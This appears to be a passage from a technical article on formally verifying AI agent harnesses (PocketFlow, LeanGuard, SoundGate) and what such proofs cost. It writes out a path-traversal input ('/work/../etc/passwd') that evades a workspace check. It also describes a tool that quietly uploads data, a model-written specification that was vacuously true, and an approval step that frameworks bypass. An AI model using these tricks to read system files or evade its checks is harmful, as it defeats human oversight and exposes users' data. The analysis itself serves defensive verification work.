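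At each step, the loop starts in a state s, receives an action a from the AI, produces an event e, and moves to a state s′. An event is either an effect on the outside world or "no effect", which the loop produces when it refuses an action. A policy Π(s, a, e, s′) is true or false for each step. The proof uses two versions of the loop, a simple one M with the policy Π_M and a detailed one I with the policy Π_I. Both must respond to every action in every state.

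**Theorem.** Assume that:

- **A1.** Every step of every run of M satisfies Π_M, whatever actions the AI chooses.
- **A2.** I *refines* M, which means that:
  - R1. I and M start in matching states.
  - R2. If I and M are in matching states and I takes a step on action a, then M can take a step on a that has a matching event and ends in a matching state.
  - R3. If M's step satisfies Π_M, the matching step of I satisfies Π_I.

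Then every step of every run of I satisfies Π_I, whatever actions the AI chooses.

To prove it, take any run of I. By R1, the starting states match. Applying R2 to each step in turn builds a run of M with the same actions. By A1, every step of that run satisfies Π_M, and by R3, the corresponding step of I satisfies Π_I. Dafny has checked this argument along with A1 and A2 for PocketFlow.

The PocketFlow policy lets the agent read files only in a workspace folder, call only approved tools and take only a limited number of steps. Suppose the folder is /work and the only approved tool is called summarise:

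| Action chosen by the AI | Event | Policy |
|---|---|---|
| read /work/notes.txt | file read | satisfied |
| read /etc/passwd | no effect | satisfied, because the loop refused |
| call delete_all | no effect | satisfied, because the loop refused |
| call summarise | tool call | satisfied |

Now suppose that the Python code of summarise also uploads its input to a web server. The loop still produces one event, the call to an approved tool, so the policy is satisfied and the theorem holds. Moon and Varshney extend the theorem to real effects only on the condition that every outside effect corresponds to an event in the formal loop. The upload violates this condition because it has no event, and so would a direct call to Python's file functions anywhere in the agent's code.

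An action can also satisfy the formal policy and still do what the developer wanted to prevent. The published Dafny lemma expresses the folder rule as `StartsWith(path, workspace_root)`. If this compares plain text, as its name suggests, the path `/work/../etc/passwd` passes, even though the operating system resolves it to `/etc/passwd`. Unless other code simplifies the path first, the agent could read the password file without breaking the policy. L3M's theorem about paths rules out this trick.

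The deployed code is Python that the Dafny compiler generates from the verified loop. Users therefore have to trust that compiler, Dafny's verifier, the Python runtime and the code that turns the AI's text into an action. Moon and Varshney fed the Python version a mixture of permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events. This test is useful evidence about the translation, but the proof covers only the formal loop.

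### A specification that checked nothing

Moon and Varshney had AI write the specifications and proofs. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the source code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the formal text and repaired proofs that Dafny rejected. A model that sees the code might simply describe what the code does and call that a safety property, so Moon and Varshney didn't show the code to the model when it wrote the property. They also ran the system without this restriction for comparison.

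One test agent answered questions from documents and was allowed to open only those on an approved list. The fixed specification template included a record of tool calls but no record of opened documents. The model that could see the code identified the mismatch and left the record of tool calls permanently empty. The property "every recorded tool call is approved" was then true because no calls were recorded. Dafny accepted the proof, and the specification also passed three automatic quality checks, two of which are meant to detect specifications that are too weak.

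The model that couldn't see the code used the record of tool calls for opened documents instead, so its proof did establish something about those documents. Moon and Varshney suggest also checking that each record can contain an entry. A person reading the specification could also catch the problem, but only by noticing that a formally correct statement is about an empty list.

### Verified rules and tested code

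*LeanGuard* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) presents another Lean program that checks tool calls before they run. Its rules can refer to earlier events, such as a customer confirming a change. Sankar and colleagues separately defined what the rules mean in temporal logic, and proved that the program allows a call only if the rules permit it under that definition. This assumes that the data the program receives about the outside world is accurate.

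LeanGuard's policies for three kinds of customer service in τ²-bench contain 45 rules in 583 lines of Lean. AI drafted the rules, and people corrected them. Without LeanGuard, agents made at least 33 calls that broke these rules, and with it they made none. The zero was guaranteed, as it was for Concordat, because the program blocks calls using the same rules that define a violation.

As a more independent measure, a language model judged the agents against the benchmark's written policy. It found violations in 9.7% of conversations without LeanGuard and 5.6% with it. The judge makes mistakes, but some remaining violations are to be expected because the Lean rules cover only the parts of the written policy that a check on tool calls can enforce.

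In *Stop Means Stop*, Khan (2026) found the same fault in all five frameworks he tested that had an approval step before actions. When an agent proposed two actions at once, one of which needed approval, the framework paused that action but carried out the other during the pause. A person who then clicked "reject" was too late to stop the other action. To fix this, Khan wrote SoundGate, a separate Rust program that must release every outside action before it happens.

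He checked SoundGate with four tools:

| Tool | What it examined | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Verus | a model of the gate handling requests in sequence | all 11 items verified |
| TLC | the model under every possible order of requests, for a few runs and actions | no violation in 74.8 million states |
| TLAPS | the model with any number of runs and actions | all 68 proof steps accepted |
| Loom | the actual Rust code with two threads running at once | three small tests, no failures |

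The abstract describes the core of the gate as "mechanically verified", but the first three tools examined a model of it. Khan tried to verify the Rust code directly with the tool Kani, but it stalled on the standard library's data structures. So he used *differential testing*, which runs the model and the real code on the same inputs and compares their results. They agreed on all 12 million random operations, which puts the rate of disagreement below about one in four million, with 95% confidence, for operations like those tested. He also compared all 14,580 possible steps for two runs with two actions each and found no differences.

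To see whether the tests could detect faults, Khan deliberately put five bugs into the Rust code. Comparison with the model caught four, and Loom caught the fifth, which appears only when two requests arrive at the same time. Random testing and model checking had already uncovered two real bugs during development, one of which could release the same action twice.

Differential testing can't rule out rare disagreements, but it tests the real program, including the standard library, which the proofs left out. For a harness written in an ordinary language, the most practical option is probably to combine a proof about a small model with differential testing.

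### What proofs cost

The seL4 kernel is the usual standard of comparison for verified software. In 2009 Gerwin Klein and colleagues published a proof that its 8,700 lines of C do what a formal specification requires. The proof was about 200,000 lines long and took roughly 20 person-years. About 11 of those went into seL4 itself, and the rest went into tools and libraries that other projects could reuse. Designing and writing the kernel had taken about 2.2 person-years.

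Klein and colleagues assumed that the C compiler, 600 lines of assembly code, the start-up code and the hardware were correct. In 2013, Thomas Sewell, Magnus Myreen and Klein removed the need to trust the compiler by proving that the machine code for one type of processor matched the C code. L3M, Agenra and the PocketFlow proof still depend on an unverified compiler.

Later tools reduced the work. The IronFleet project at Microsoft Research took about 3.7 person-years to develop a method for verifying distributed systems in Dafny and apply it to two systems. Moon and Varshney organised their proof the same way, but AI wrote most of the formal text. They ran their system four times on two small agents. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens, which probably cost less than $100. Dafny took at most 2.5 seconds to check each path through an agent.

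At seL4's rate of 11 person-years for 8,700 lines, a proof about 100 lines of code would take a person six or seven weeks. This comparison overstates how much work the AI system saves, because PocketFlow's policy has three simple rules, while seL4's specification describes the behaviour of an entire kernel. The token count also excludes the work of designing the AI system, the template and the main theorem, which was done before the runs began.

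AI has therefore made it easy to write the proof for a small, well-defined part of a harness. Stronger models than Opus 4.7 were available by late 2026 and could probably handle larger parts. AI reduces the rest of the work by less. In these projects, the proofs didn't catch an empty record, a missing rule about where a message came from, and a tool that did more than its description covered. A developer who wants a verified mediator can expect to spend most of the effort on the policy, the tool descriptions and tests of the running system.
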